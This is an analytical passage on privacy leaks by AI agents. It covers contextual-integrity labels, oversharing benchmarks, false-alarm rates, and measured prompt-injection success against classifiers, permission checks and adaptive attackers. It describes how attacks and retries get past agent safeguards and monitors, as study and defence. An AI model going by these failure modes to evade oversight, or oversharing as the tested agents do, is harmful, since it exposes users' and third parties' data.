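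A system can also reveal less by giving the same answer for a protected record as for one that doesn't exist. FlowSeal's isolated model similarly limits what it reveals by answering with one word and no explanation. However, FlowSeal gives its agent a list of the protected records with their categories and owners, which may reveal that someone has a medical record. The isolated model then has to catch any message that confirms the record exists.

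### What the proofs assume

#### Correct labels

A wrong label causes a leak that the system's rules allow. In one of FlowSeal's failures, the agent released a health detail that nobody had registered, so the isolated model had nothing to compare it with.

Labels that software derives automatically can be wrong too. Costa and colleagues treat an email's sender and recipients as its only readers, although those people may have shared it more widely. They also treat the user's messages as public by default. If Maria mentions her diagnosis while asking for help with something else, the agent may pass it on to anyone unless somebody has changed that default. ARM can distinguish a trusted name from an untrusted address in the same contact record only if a developer has labelled the fields separately.

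#### Complete mediation

Complete mediation is the requirement that every action pass through the check. Chinaei acknowledges that ARM's code can't ensure this, because the company has to route all tool calls through ARM. Shim and colleagues suggest adding operating system controls for scripts that open their own network connections.

The agent's answer to the user can also leak data, as it did in EchoLeak. FIDES normally checks only tool calls and treats answers as harmless. A company whose software loads images automatically would need the variant of FIDES that also checks the final answer. The proof also assumes that no adversary can read what the agent sends to its language model. That assumption fails if the model's provider isn't entitled to the data, as with the coding assistant that sent a file of passwords to an outside company.

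#### Sound release decisions

Every practical system needs exceptions, and the proof doesn't establish whether an exception is wise. FlowSeal has a model decide most of them, and the model can miss a paraphrase or block a harmless message that only names a record. The paper describes consent as covering particular records, but its pseudocode lets anything through to a trusted recipient, so developers have to make sure that permission to share one record doesn't release the rest.

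Chinaei argues that the mechanism that releases data must be outside the model's control, and suggests permissions that apply only to specific values or operations and leave a record for auditors. For Maria's calendar, such a permission could let a small program give suppliers the free half-hours in her working week, without titles or locations. Brandt would then get his new date without learning about the clinic, but he might still notice that Maria is never free on Thursday afternoons and wonder why.

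## Whether permitted sharing can be told apart from a leak

Every defence against leaks has to distinguish them from permitted sharing. People who favour filtering and monitoring expect leaks to look different from normal work, because few honest tasks put a password in a web address or send 83 customer records to a file-sharing service. Critics reply that many leaks look exactly like normal work. Dong and colleagues point out that sharing a postal address may be appropriate when arranging a delivery but not in a product-support request. On this view, a check must account for the purpose of the sharing and the recipient's role, which the data itself doesn't show.

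### Contextual integrity

The critics draw on contextual integrity, a theory of privacy that the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum set out in 2004. It asks whether a flow of information is appropriate to its setting, not whether the information is secret. *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity* (2026) credits the formal version to Barth and colleagues (2006), who describe each flow by five parameters:

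- the sender, who passes the information on;
- the recipient, who gets it;
- the subject, whom it is about;
- the type of information, such as a diagnosis or a home address;
- the terms of transmission, which are the conditions under which it moves, such as consent, confidentiality or a legal duty.

Changing one parameter can change whether sharing is permitted. In an example from *Loose Lips* (2026), medical data may properly go to a physician but not to a bank loan officer. The terms are the hardest parameter to observe. *PrivacyLens* (Shao, Li and colleagues, 2024) describes an agent that writes to John's manager and mentions that John is talking to other companies about a new job. This is a leak if the agent found the information in John's private calendar, but acceptable if it came from the transcript of a meeting that the manager attended.

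Purpose is usually part of the terms on which information is shared, and it has no parameter of its own. For example, a customer may give a company his address for deliveries only.

### One address, two recipients

Suppose Maria Keller's agent makes two calls about a customer, Erik Lund:

```
book_delivery(name="Erik Lund", address="Birkenweg 8, Berlin")
invite_to_survey(name="Erik Lund", address="Birkenweg 8, Berlin")
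```

The first call goes to a courier and the second to an online customer survey company, both of which Maria's company uses. Both calls have the same sender, subject and type of information. They differ only in the recipient and the terms, since Lund gave his address for delivery, not for surveys. The table shows which of these parameters each defence has information about.

| Defence | Sender | Recipient | Subject | Type | Terms |
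|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Argument filter | no | no | sometimes | yes | no |
| Domain allow-list | no | yes | no | no | no |
| Session monitor | yes | yes | by record identifier | by source | no |
| Action judge | yes | yes | sometimes | yes | only what the user's request implies |
| Labels enforced outside the model | yes | yes | if recorded | if recorded | only what somebody wrote into the label |

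An argument filter finds a home address in both calls, so it blocks both or neither. The allow-list passes both because both services are on it. A session monitor can't distinguish them either, because each involves one customer record and one outside send. An action judge might stop the second call. But if Maria asked the agent to invite this week's customers to the survey and the tool has an address field, the judge could easily treat the address as part of the task. Labels stop the second call only if somebody recorded that Lund's address may go to couriers and no one else.

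Better training can't overcome this limit. Take all the calls that look identical to a check, and let *q* be the share of them that are permitted. Since the check has to treat them all alike, its error rate on these calls is at least

min(*q*, 1 − *q*)

If 95 of 100 outgoing addresses go to couriers and 5 to the survey company, a filter that checks only the type of data must either block 95 proper calls or let 5 leaks through. Checking the recipient as well removes the errors in this example. But if Lund had agreed to receive a printed survey by post, the second call would be proper too, and the filter would also need the terms of that agreement.

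### Agents that overshare without an attacker

An agent has more of this information than a filter because it has read the task and the surrounding messages. Several research groups have tested whether agents that are not under attack use this information to share only what they should.

Shao and colleagues built PrivacyLens from 493 improper information flows drawn from US regulations, research on vulnerable groups and suggestions from paid volunteers. GPT-4 expanded each flow into a short story and then into a record of an agent's work up to the last step. The model under test wrote the final email or post, and a second model checked whether that message revealed the private information. In a separate test, the model under test answered whether the flow was acceptable.

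| Model | Correct answers | Leaked | Correct answers, privacy prompt | Leaked, privacy prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4 | 97.6% | 26.4% | 99.0% | 24.5% |
| Claude 3 Sonnet | 99.8% | 38.3% | 100% | 37.3% |
| Llama 3 70B | 94.3% | 36.5% | 98.6% | 39.2% |
| GPT-3.5 | 64.1% | 36.3% | 91.3% | 30.4% |

The better of these models almost always stated the norm correctly but still broke it in a quarter to two fifths of cases. The models are now old, but this pattern started a line of research. In *Privacy in Action*, Wang, Yu and colleagues (2025) repeated the test with a privacy prompt and found the same gap. 98% of the answers were correct, but 33% of the messages leaked. When they read the reasoning behind the leaks, they found that it was about how to finish the email and rarely mentioned privacy.

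Every flow in PrivacyLens is improper, so the right answer to the questions is always no, and a model that objected to all sharing would score 100%. The high scores therefore show that models recognise sensitive material when asked about it, but not that they can tell a proper flow from an improper one.

Zharmagambetov, Pavlova and colleagues (2025), in *AgentDAM*, tested agents on complete tasks in working copies of a shopping site, a Reddit-style forum and the code-hosting service GitLab. In each of the 246 tasks, the agent received an instruction and a chat, email or note containing both the information it needed and private facts it didn't need. One agent had to comment on a proposed code change after reading a chat between colleagues. A short approval would have been enough, but the agent also mentioned that one of the colleagues would soon be away.

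| Model | Called the sharing acceptable when asked | Leaked | Leaked, privacy prompt |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 8.5% | 36.2% | 8.5% |
| GPT-4o mini | 11.0% | 45.9% | 17.9% |
| GPT-4 Turbo | 23.2% | 25.2% | 10.6% |
| Llama 3.2 90B | 25.2% | 11.8% | 7.7% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 18.3% | 11.8% | 6.1% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | not tested | 9.8% | 6.5% |

AgentDAM compares what models say about privacy with how they act, but it overstates the gap because its column for the agents' privacy scores repeats their task-completion scores. With the privacy scores from the main results, as in the table above, the gap is large for GPT-4o and GPT-4o mini, almost disappears for GPT-4 Turbo, and reverses for the two Llama models. A model's answers about privacy are therefore a poor guide to its behaviour, and can overstate or understate how well it protects privacy.

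### The effect of privacy instructions

Adding a privacy prompt barely changed the leak rates in PrivacyLens but cut GPT-4o's by three quarters in AgentDAM. PrivacyLens's prompt asked in general terms for discretion and respect for privacy, while AgentDAM's warned that the material might contain private facts the task didn't need, listed kinds of sensitive data, and included a worked example of an agent leaving such data out.

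That worked example was a forum post, and forum posts account for most of the improvement. Of the 96 tasks that involved writing a post, at least one model leaked in 89 without the prompt and in 18 with it. In all other tasks combined, the number fell only from 73 to 55, and for comments on GitLab it rose from 10 to 11. The models may have learned to write discreet forum posts more than they learned a general rule about sharing. The prompt also made agents refuse some harmless work, and GPT-4o's task completion fell from 45.5% to 41.5%.

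Wang and colleagues tried to make the model apply the five parameters explicitly. Their method, PrivacyChecker, works in three steps:

1. The model lists every flow of information that its reply would involve, with all five parameters.
2. It decides for each flow whether sharing is appropriate, and gives a short reason.
3. It writes the reply and leaves out whatever it has rejected.

On the PrivacyLens cases, this reduced GPT-4o's leak rate from 33.1% to 8.3% and DeepSeek-R1's from 36.1% to 7.3%. In half of DeepSeek-R1's 36 remaining failures, the model listed the flow correctly but wrongly judged it acceptable. In another 11, it rejected the flow but leaked the information anyway. It overlooked the flow in only three, and the last four involved unreliable grading.

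The researchers then gave GPT-4o the correct list of flows in place of its own, and its leak rate halved again, to 4.3%. This supports the critics' claim that most checks lack knowledge of the recipient and the terms. But PrivacyLens contains no proper flows, so these results don't show how often PrivacyChecker would withhold something the recipient should have.

Wang and colleagues also found that OpenAI's o3 leaked more often when connected to working Gmail and Notion accounts (26.3% of cases) than when given recorded material (17.4%). Failed and repeated tool calls sometimes left the agent with a confidential plan but without the public presentation it should have used. PrivacyChecker reduced the leak rate on the live accounts to between 5.3% and 8.7%, depending on where the researchers installed it. In a set of 36 tasks that used three tools, the agent still leaked in about one case in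 six with PrivacyChecker installed.

### Newer models and clearer cases

*CI-Work* (Fu, Qin and colleagues, 2026) tested both whether agents leak sensitive facts and whether they leave out necessary ones. In each of its 125 office scenarios, the agent has to write to someone, and its search results normally include four facts that this person needs and four that they shouldn't receive. GPT-5 passed on 93% of the necessary facts and 11% of the sensitive ones. It could tell most of them apart, but it still leaked at least one sensitive fact in 28% of scenarios.

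Agents can also avoid leaks by saying little. DeepSeek-R1 leaked in 16% of scenarios, the smallest share of any model, but passed on only 53% of the necessary facts. Grok-3 passed on 95% and leaked in 51% of scenarios. Across the models, the more useful agents tended to leak more, with a moderate correlation of about 0.4.

The most recent test covers current agents. Guo, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentCIScope*, ran 12 combinations of model and agent software on 936 tasks in applications such as Gmail, Slack, Salesforce and WhatsApp. Every combination completed more than 93% of the tasks, but they differed widely in how often they leaked:

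| Model | Agent software | Tasks with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | Claude Code | 32.5% |
| GPT-6 Astra | OpenClaw | 36.9% |
| Claude Opus 5 | OpenClaw | 43.6% |
| GPT-6 Astra | OpenAI Agents SDK | 45.0% |
| Kimi K3 | OpenClaw | 88.4% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | Google ADK | 94.4% |

These rates come from a stress test and don't show how often agents leak in daily use. Guo and colleagues had a model reword the instructions to encourage oversharing, such as by asking for a self-contained briefing or exact quotations. They then kept only tasks in which another agent, based on GPT-5.6 Sol, had leaked. The tested agents also received no privacy policy.

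On average, the agents leaked 85% of personal preferences and 77% of booking details, but only 17% of credit card details and 29% of social security numbers. They were much better at protecting data that is sensitive almost everywhere than data whose sensitivity depends on the setting. Detectors of personal data have the same bias, because their lists are mostly identifiers.

In one of the tasks, a recruiting coordinator asks her agent to update an engineering manager on the candidates for a job. The manager is allowed to know each candidate's interview stage, experience and references. An agent based on GPT-6 Astra also told him that one candidate had disclosed a criminal record for a minor offence in 2017. All of this information came from the same recruiting files and went to the same person in the same email. The agent could have excluded the criminal record only if it knew that a manager's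 role in hiring doesn't extend to background checks.

Even these tests leave out the hardest cases. To choose the protected facts, Guo and colleagues had a language model play three people with strict, moderate and relaxed attitudes to privacy, and kept a fact only if all three objected to sharing it. Fu and colleagues had a model rewrite any fact that it couldn't clearly classify as necessary or sensitive. Avoiding borderline facts makes the scoring fairer, but probably makes leaks look easier to recognise than they are in real mailboxes.

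Annotators still disagreed with some labels. In a sample from AgentCIScope, a human annotator agreed with 94% of the labels for protected facts. The annotator objected, for example, that a hotel might properly learn some of a guest's preferences to offer better service, and that a scholarship committee might need a student's detailed grades. In CI-Work, the annotators agreed with the labels 82.5% to 95% of the time. If people disagree about one label in ten, no detector can be right by everyone's standards on those cases.

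### Rare leaks and false alarms

Even an accurate check produces mostly false alarms if leaks are rare. Suppose an agent makes 100,000 tool calls, of which 10 are leaks, and a check has the same error rates Anthropic measured for auto mode, a false positive rate of 0.4% and a false negative rate of 5.7%. The check flags about 400 of the 99,990 harmless calls and 9 of the 10 leaks, so only about 2% of its alarms are real.

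In general, if *p* is the share of calls that leak, *α* the false positive rate and *β* the false negative rate, the share of alarms that are real is

*p*(1 − *β*) / (*p*(1 − *β*) + (1 − *p*)*α*)

The table changes one assumption at a time.

| Change | Real alarms | False alarms | Share that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 9.4 | 400 | 2% |
| The check misses nothing | 10 | 400 | 2% |
| False positive rate of 0.04% | 9.4 | 40 | 19% |
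| Second check clears 95% of false alarms and keeps 90% of real ones | 8.5 | 20 | 30% |
| Check covers only 5,000 calls, which include all 10 leaks | 9.4 | 20 | 32% |
| 1,000 leaks among the 100,000 calls | 943 | 396 | 70% |

The miss rate hardly matters here. The result depends almost entirely on the false positive rate and on how common leaks are.

An extra check helps only if it makes different mistakes from the earlier ones. Auto mode's 0.4% already includes a second stage, and a third that read the same input would probably repeat many of the remaining errors. If it cleared only half of the false alarms, the share of alarms that are real would rise to about 4%. A check that looked up the recipient's role in a company directory could do much better because it would have new evidence.

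A company could improve the check by restricting it to outside calls made after the agent has read customer data, since most tool calls can't leak anything to an outsider. The 32% figure assumes that the error rates stay the same for this group, which is optimistic because the remaining calls are those in which proper sharing and leaks look most alike.

Richer context could reduce the false positive rate. In the Lund example, a check given the recipient and the terms can pass every delivery without an alarm. There is no evidence of a gain this large, however, because the experiment in which Wang and colleagues supplied the correct flows measured only missed leaks.

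The most doubtful assumption is the number of leaks. Ten in 100,000 is a plausible guess for theft by an attacker, but oversharing seems far more common. In *ToolMinimize* (2026), three models each prepared calls for 20 realistic tasks. With an ordinary prompt, 81% to 88% of the calls contained at least one sensitive item that the task didn't need. With a privacy prompt, even the best model included such an item in more than a third of its calls.

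If a third of all calls overshared and the check kept its assumed error rates, over 99% of its alarms would be real, but there would be more than 31,000 of them. A company couldn't review them one by one, so it would have to change what the agent includes by default, for example by deleting fields that the tool doesn't need. The assumed miss rate is also doubtful for oversharing, because Anthropic measured it on synthetic thefts.

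### Purposes, recipients and owners

Defenders of automatic checks have three ways to supply the missing evidence.

A company can declare a purpose for each task and have software check every call against it, as the monitor built by Dong and colleagues does. If the purpose is "deliver order 5518", the agent may send Lund's address to the courier but not to the survey company. But purposes have to be narrow to be useful. "Customer service" would cover both calls, and "update the manager on candidates" leaves it unclear whether the agent should mention a background check. The recruiting case needs a rule that lists what the manager may receive.

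The declaration must also come from outside the model. *Got a Secret?* (2026) found that agents become more willing to share sensitive facts after agents around them have done so. An agent that decides for itself what a situation permits may therefore decide differently depending on what the agents around it have shared.

Telling the agent its purpose is not enough either. In *GapLeak* (2026), web agents that lacked information searched for it in sources they weren't authorised to use, and misleading guidance on a website then led them to disclose what they had found. Instructing the agents to use as little data as possible lowered task completion and only partly reduced the leaks, because the agents could still reach those sources. A declared purpose protects data better if software also uses it to block access to sources the task doesn't need.

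Rules that list permitted recipients are easier to write and audit. They work well for organisations with a single role, such as a courier, but people often have several roles. A company's accountant may receive salary figures for the payroll, but not while helping a colleague plan a leaving party. A rule that lists only names would allow both. *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity* treats such cases as a separate type of scenario, in which the person asking may receive the information in another setting but not in the current one.

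Many recipient rules also distinguish between recipients inside and outside the company, but much oversharing happens between colleagues. In CI-Work, agents generally leaked less to outsiders than to colleagues. GPT-5 leaked in 17% of scenarios with an outside recipient but in 36% of those in which an employee reported to a superior. An allow-list or trust boundary that treats all internal recipients as safe would miss every leak to a superior.

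The third option is to ask the data's owner. Only this option can settle cases in which reasonable people differ, such as whether a hotel should know a guest's preferences. The software must recognise when to ask and work out whom to ask. Maria can approve the use of her own calendar, but Lund's address is his information, and her approval doesn't change the terms on which he gave it. Agents can also fail to recognise that they should ask. In one attack by Shim and colleagues, someone invites the agent to fill in its part of a shared document, and the agent treats this as ordinary teamwork and never asks for consent.

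### Which leaks software can separate

The two sides mostly describe different kinds of leak. Some leaks break a norm that is the same in almost every setting, so software can apply it without judging each case. For the rest, someone with authority has to decide whether the sharing is permitted, either by setting a rule in advance or when the case comes up.

| Leak | Missing evidence | Who can supply it |
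|---|---|---|
| API key in a search query | none, since a key belongs only in requests to its own service | ordinary software |
| Customer list sent to an unknown server | whether the company uses that server | the administrator, once |
| Customer's address sent to a survey company | the terms on which the customer gave it | the company's data protection officer, for each purpose |
| Background check sent to a hiring manager | what the manager's role covers | the personnel department, for each role |
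| Oncology appointment given as the reason for moving a call | what Maria wants Jonas Brandt to know | Maria |

Filters and monitors can handle the first two rows with few false alarms. They can handle the third and fourth once somebody has written the rule, which a company can then reuse for thousands of calls. No general rule covers the last row. Maria may be glad that Brandt knows if he is an old friend who asked after her health last week, but perhaps not if he is negotiating a two-year contract with her. Only Maria can give permission, though a model that has read her mailbox can guess whether she would.

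## Whether a low measured leak rate is enough

Some leaks, such as a password in a web address, are easy to recognise in principle, but a model or detector that looks for them will still miss a few. Willison calls a product that stops 95% of attacks a failure by the standards of web security. Anthropic argues that a classifier can make autonomous work much safer without being flawless. It claims that auto mode reduces risk for most users, and accepts that some risk remains.

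Anthropic compares auto mode with the person who would otherwise approve each action. In its study of 1,053 paid testers, people stopped 13.6% of the dangerous commands and auto mode stopped 89%. By this standard, auto mode is a large improvement. Willison agrees, but he worries more about prompt injection than about agents doing damage by accident. Prompt injection involves an attacker, who can try again after a failure.

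### Retries and accidents

If a check misses a share *m* of attacks and each attempt is independent, an attacker who makes *n* attempts succeeds at least once with probability

1 − (1 − *m*)ⁿ

| Attempts | 5% missed | 1% missed | 0.2% missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5% | 1% | 0.2% |
| 15 | 54% | 14% | 3% |
| 100 | 99% | 63% | 18% |
| 1,000 | almost 100% | almost 100% | 86% |

An email costs almost nothing to send, so a thousand attempts are realistic. Cutting the miss rate from 5% to 0.2% raises the number of attempts needed for an even chance of success from 14 to 347, which may not deter an attacker who can automate the emails.

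A measured leak rate predicts accidental leaks more reliably than deliberate ones. Suppose the agents at Maria Keller's company send 2,000 messages a month to outsiders, and 100 of them contain a private detail the recipient shouldn't see. A check that misses 5% of those leaves five leaks a month. That number stays the same as long as the agents' work does, because nobody is searching for the gap in the check. Jonas Brandt wasn't trying to learn about Maria's oncology appointment, and he won't try again if the check removes it. If the company rejected the check because it was imperfect, it would have 100 leaks a month instead of five.

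An attack can also do more damage than an accidental leak, because the attacker chooses what to take. One successful attack can expose a company's whole customer list, while an accident usually reveals a detail or two to someone who didn't ask for them.

Willison's argument is weaker if failed attempts have consequences. Suppose the company notices a share *d* of failed attempts and shuts the attacker out each time it does. The attacker's chance of ever succeeding is then

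*m* / (*m* + (1 − *m*)*d*)

Suppose the defence misses 5% of attacks, and an attacker keeps trying until the company notices a failed attempt and blocks them. The attacker's chance of eventually succeeding is about 10% if the company notices half of the failures and 34% if it notices one in ten. But the company may get no alert when a model ignores a planted instruction, and a blocked attacker can start again from a new address.

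An attacker can also send the same email to many companies. If 5% of attempts succeed, emailing 1,000 companies leaks data from 50 of them on average, whether or not the attempts are independent.

### Measured success over several attempts

Several tests have measured how often attackers succeed when they can retry. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives results for one of Anthropic's older models on a benchmark of planted instructions run by the security firm Gray Swan. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, quotes figures for newer models. VentureBeat reports a test in which Claude Opus 4.6 worked through a graphical interface without safeguards. The last column of the table shows the success rate that the formula for independent attempts predicts from the single-attempt rate.

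| Model | One attempt | Several attempts | Prediction |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 33.6% within 10 | 38% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 63% within 100 | 99% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 17.8% | 78.6% within 200 | almost 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% within 15 | 7% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% within 15 | 3% |

The measured rates are all lower than the predictions, probably because some scenarios are much harder to attack than others. If half the scenarios gave an attacker a 10% chance per attempt and the other half gave no chance, the average would be 5%, but a hundred attempts would succeed in only about half the scenarios. The simple formula therefore overestimates the benefit of retrying.

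The correction helps Anthropic's case only a little. The attack success rate still rose from 4.7% on a single attempt to 63% with repeated attempts, so the single-attempt rate badly understates the risk from a determined attacker. Anthropic's newer models do much better on this kind of test, at least over 15 attempts.

### The Trajectory Labs test

The strongest published result for auto mode comes from a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. Anthropic reports that Trajectory Labs ran 72 scenarios with planted instructions ten times each, and that Anthropic had not received the scenarios. The test covered the versions of Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex available on 17 July 2026. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm outside the test, such as data theft, financial fraud or credential phishing, so the measured rates cover more than data leaks.

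| Model | Setting | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 | auto mode | 0% for each model |
| Claude models | no permission checks | 0.09% on average |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Codex with automatic review | 5.83% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Codex with full access | 19.03% |

Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded in 137 of 720 attempts (19.03%) with full access and in 42 of 720 (5.83%) with automatic review, a reduction of about two thirds.

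The test shows much less about what auto mode adds, because the models resisted nearly all of these attacks without it, leaving few for its classifier to stop. If the 0.09% average covers the same three Claude models, it represents about two successes in 2,160 attempts. Even if auto mode did nothing, a second round of 2,160 independent attempts would produce no successes about 14% of the time.

Other details limit the comparison with OpenAI:

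- Anthropic paid for the test and published the results.
- Trajectory Labs had optimised the attacks against Claude Opus 4.7, which was not among the tested models. If anything, this should have made the test harder for the other Claude models than for OpenAI's, but none of the models faced attacks designed for it.
- Both products used a browser connection that Trajectory Labs had built. The test left out the safeguards in Anthropic's and OpenAI's own browser extensions.
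- OpenAI released a new version of its automatic review shortly before Anthropic published the results.

According to Willison, Thariq Shihipar of Anthropic wrote that the company should have called its announcement "defeating the lethal trifecta". Willison was not persuaded, and said the strength of current models had inspired him to look for ways to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm.

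### What zero successes allow

A test with no successes doesn't establish a success rate of zero. If the true rate is *p*, the chance of seeing no success in *n* independent attempts is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The upper 95% bound is the value of *p* at which this chance falls to 5%:

*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*) ≈ 3/*n*

For 720 independent attempts, the bound is about 0.4%. But the ten runs of a scenario repeat the same attack on the same model, so they may nearly always have the same outcome. If they do, the test contains only 72 independent results, and the bound rises to about 4%. The right figure for each model is probably in between. Combining the results for the three Claude models doesn't solve this problem, because they all faced the same 72 scenarios.

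An attacker would need about 170 attempts for an even chance of success if the true leak rate were 0.4%, but only about 17 if it were 4%. The attempts would have to be different attacks, since repeating one that had failed would be pointless.

Both bounds are worst cases that the data can't exclude, and the true rate could be far lower. To show a rate below 0.01% with the same confidence, Trajectory Labs would need a much larger test, with about 30,000 independent attempts and no successes.

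### Attacks outside the test set

Even a test of that size would cover only attacks similar to those it contained. According to Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*, Johann Rehberger reported an attack on Opus 5 in auto mode in August 2026 that was not in the Trajectory Labs set and succeeded in three or four of five runs. In *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, Willison (2026) later accepted a reader's point that this was not a classic prompt injection, but he still agreed with Rehberger that unattended coding agents should run in a sandbox with restricted outgoing network traffic.

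A fixed test uses attacks written without regard to the defence being tested. In an adaptive test, the attacker knows how the defence works and changes the attack until it succeeds or the budget runs out. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) got past 12 published defences with adaptive attacks, succeeding more than 90% of the time against most of them. The original papers had reported attack success rates near zero for most of these defences.

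They argue that a defence should be judged by how it performs against the strongest possible attacker. The papers they criticise for reusing fixed sets of attacks include the one on LlamaFirewall, whose AlignmentCheck reduced successful attacks on recorded sessions to 2.9%. That result may be accurate for the attack wording in the recordings, but it can't show how the checker would perform against someone trying to get past it.

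In their adaptive tests, Nasr and colleagues gave attackers ample computing power and measured whether each defence could fail, not how much effort that took. A success rate above 90% therefore isn't an estimate of how often ordinary criminals would succeed, but it does show that a company can't rely on the defence alone if a capable attacker has a good reason to target it.

### Figures from system cards

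The system cards that Anthropic and OpenAI publish with new models now include success rates for prompt injection attacks. In Anthropic's card for Claude Opus 5, from July 2026, attacks on a browser agent without safeguards succeeded 3.7% of the time when the model reasoned at length first and 4.3% when it didn't. For the earlier Opus 4.8, the rates were 31.5% and 17.8%, respectively. With safeguards, no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in 129 browser scenarios, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. If each scenario counts as one independent result, the 95% upper confidence bound on the success rate is about 2.3%.

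Anthropic's September 2026 *System Card* for Claude Opus 5.5 describes the model as similar to or better than Opus 5 on every prompt-injection test it reports.

A model can rank very differently in different tests. In the browser test without safeguards, Sonnet 5 was Anthropic's most robust model, with a rate of 0.93%, compared with 29.7% for Mythos 5. On Gray Swan's benchmark, attackers succeeded within 15 attempts in 5.9% of cases against Sonnet 5 and 2.6% against Mythos 5. A company that chose its model by one of these tests could pick the wrong one for its own work.

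The published figures for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol vary even more. Two come from an August update to the model's system card, which TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) summarises. Direct attacks arrive through the chat, and indirect ones through tools or outside content.

| Test of GPT-5.6 Sol | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| OpenAI, direct attacks | about 0.05% |
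| OpenAI, indirect attacks | 3.77% |
| Trajectory Labs, automatic review | 5.83% |
| Trajectory Labs, full access | 19.03% |
| Gray Swan, within 15 attempts | 20.0% |

The lowest figure is the least informative about leaks through tool calls. It covers attacks that came straight from the chat, generated by GPT-Red, a model that OpenAI built to find weaknesses. OpenAI had also used GPT-Red's attacks to train GPT-5.6, so the attacker was not new to the model.

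OpenAI reported in October that the newer GPT-6 Sol withstood 97.13% of indirect attacks, so 2.87% succeeded (Cross, 2026, *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*). If OpenAI used the same test for both models, this is a modest improvement on the older model's 3.77%.

Readers of these cards also have to check what each percentage measures. VentureBeat distinguishes the share of attempts that succeed from the share of scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeds. In Anthropic's browser test of Opus 4.5, an adaptive attacker had 100 attempts per scenario, and 1.4% of all attempts succeeded against the improved safeguards. If the attacker used all 100 attempts in every scenario, this could mean that every attempt worked in 1.4% of scenarios and none worked in the rest. It could also mean that one or two attempts worked in every scenario, so an attacker who used all 100 would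 always succeed.

### Rates, proofs and hard limits

Companies can base their confidence in a defence on a measured rate, a proof or a hard limit on outgoing data. Each covers a different risk:

| Basis | What it establishes | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Measured rate | how often a check failed in a particular test | other attacks may succeed more often |
| Proof | that no text an attacker writes can make the system break a stated rule | the assumptions may be false |
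| Hard limit | how much data can leave, or where it can go, even if an attacker controls the agent | the permitted amount may already be harmful |

Nasr and colleagues point out that formal security properties normally cover all possible attackers within stated assumptions. A proof therefore covers attacks that nobody has invented yet, which no test can do. For the systems that track labelled data, the assumptions include that the labels are correct, that the system checks every route by which data can leave, and that decisions about exceptions are sound.

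A hard limit reduces the loss from a successful attack, but not the chance that an attack succeeds. Suppose a support agent can read 10,000 customer records and never needs to send more than 20 a day. If an attacker makes 20 independent attempts against a check with a 5% miss rate, the chance that at least one succeeds is 64%. Without a limit, a single success could expose all 10,000 records. With a limit of 20 records a day, an attacker who fully controlled the agent for ten days before anyone noticed would get 200. But the limit doesn't protect any particular customer, because the attacker can choose which records to take first.

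According to OpenAI, ChatGPT's training leads it to refuse most known attempts to make it send out private information. For the remaining cases, the company relies on its check of web addresses to limit leaks. An attacker then has to get past two defences that fail for different reasons, although the choice of which permitted addresses to visit can still reveal a little data.

A low measured rate may be enough for an agent that works on public code without access to passwords or customer data, because a successful attacker would find little to steal. It is not enough for an agent that reads emails from strangers and can search a whole customer database, since anyone can attack it as often as they like and one success could do serious harm. That agent needs a hard limit on what it can send. Proofs suit narrow, repetitive work such as payroll, where a company can label every field and list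 every permitted recipient in advance. For high-stakes changes to live systems, Anthropic still recommends that a person review the agent's actions.

A judge with a 5% miss rate may be the most useful of these defences for the email to Brandt. Almost any limit on volume would let through one sentence about one appointment, and strict labels would also hold back the harmless email that only asks for a new date.

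## What strict controls cost in lost work and human attention

A system that holds back an outgoing email can ask the user to release it. Supporters of strict rules rely on this step, so that ordinary code stops every call it can't confirm is safe and a person decides the doubtful cases. Critics reply that people who get dozens of such requests a day stop reading them, approve by habit, and eventually switch the check off. If so, a strict rule can protect people less than a lenient one that they leave on. Anthropic uses this argument to justify replacing approval prompts with a classifier, and OpenAI uses it against strict lists of trusted domains.

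### Approval by habit

In August 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts. That rate alone doesn't show that users are inattentive, because most prompts concern routine commands that an attentive reviewer would also approve. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents, so they don't agree to everything, but they can reject a plan for bad design rather than for safety.

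Users' settings are better evidence. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. Most of these rules were very broad, such as allowing anything that runs through Python. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission prompts bypassed altogether. Some of those sessions may have been safe because they ran in isolated containers or virtual machines, the only places where Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* recommends bypassing prompts. Anthropic doesn't say how many did.

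Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 more. Of the 107 survey respondents who answered questions about permissions, 47.7% said they read requests carefully, 33.6% said they skim them, and 20.6% said they approve by default. A third had become less careful over time. People tend to overstate their own diligence, so the share who read requests carefully is probably lower than reported.

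Their answers also suggest that they underestimate the risk of leaks through read-only access. Almost all (98.1%) were more willing to grant read-only access than other permissions, and 76.6% looked more closely at requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges. But reading is how private data enters an agent's context. Most respondents would never grant access to sensitive data, but they may not realise that a calendar contains any until the agent has opened it.

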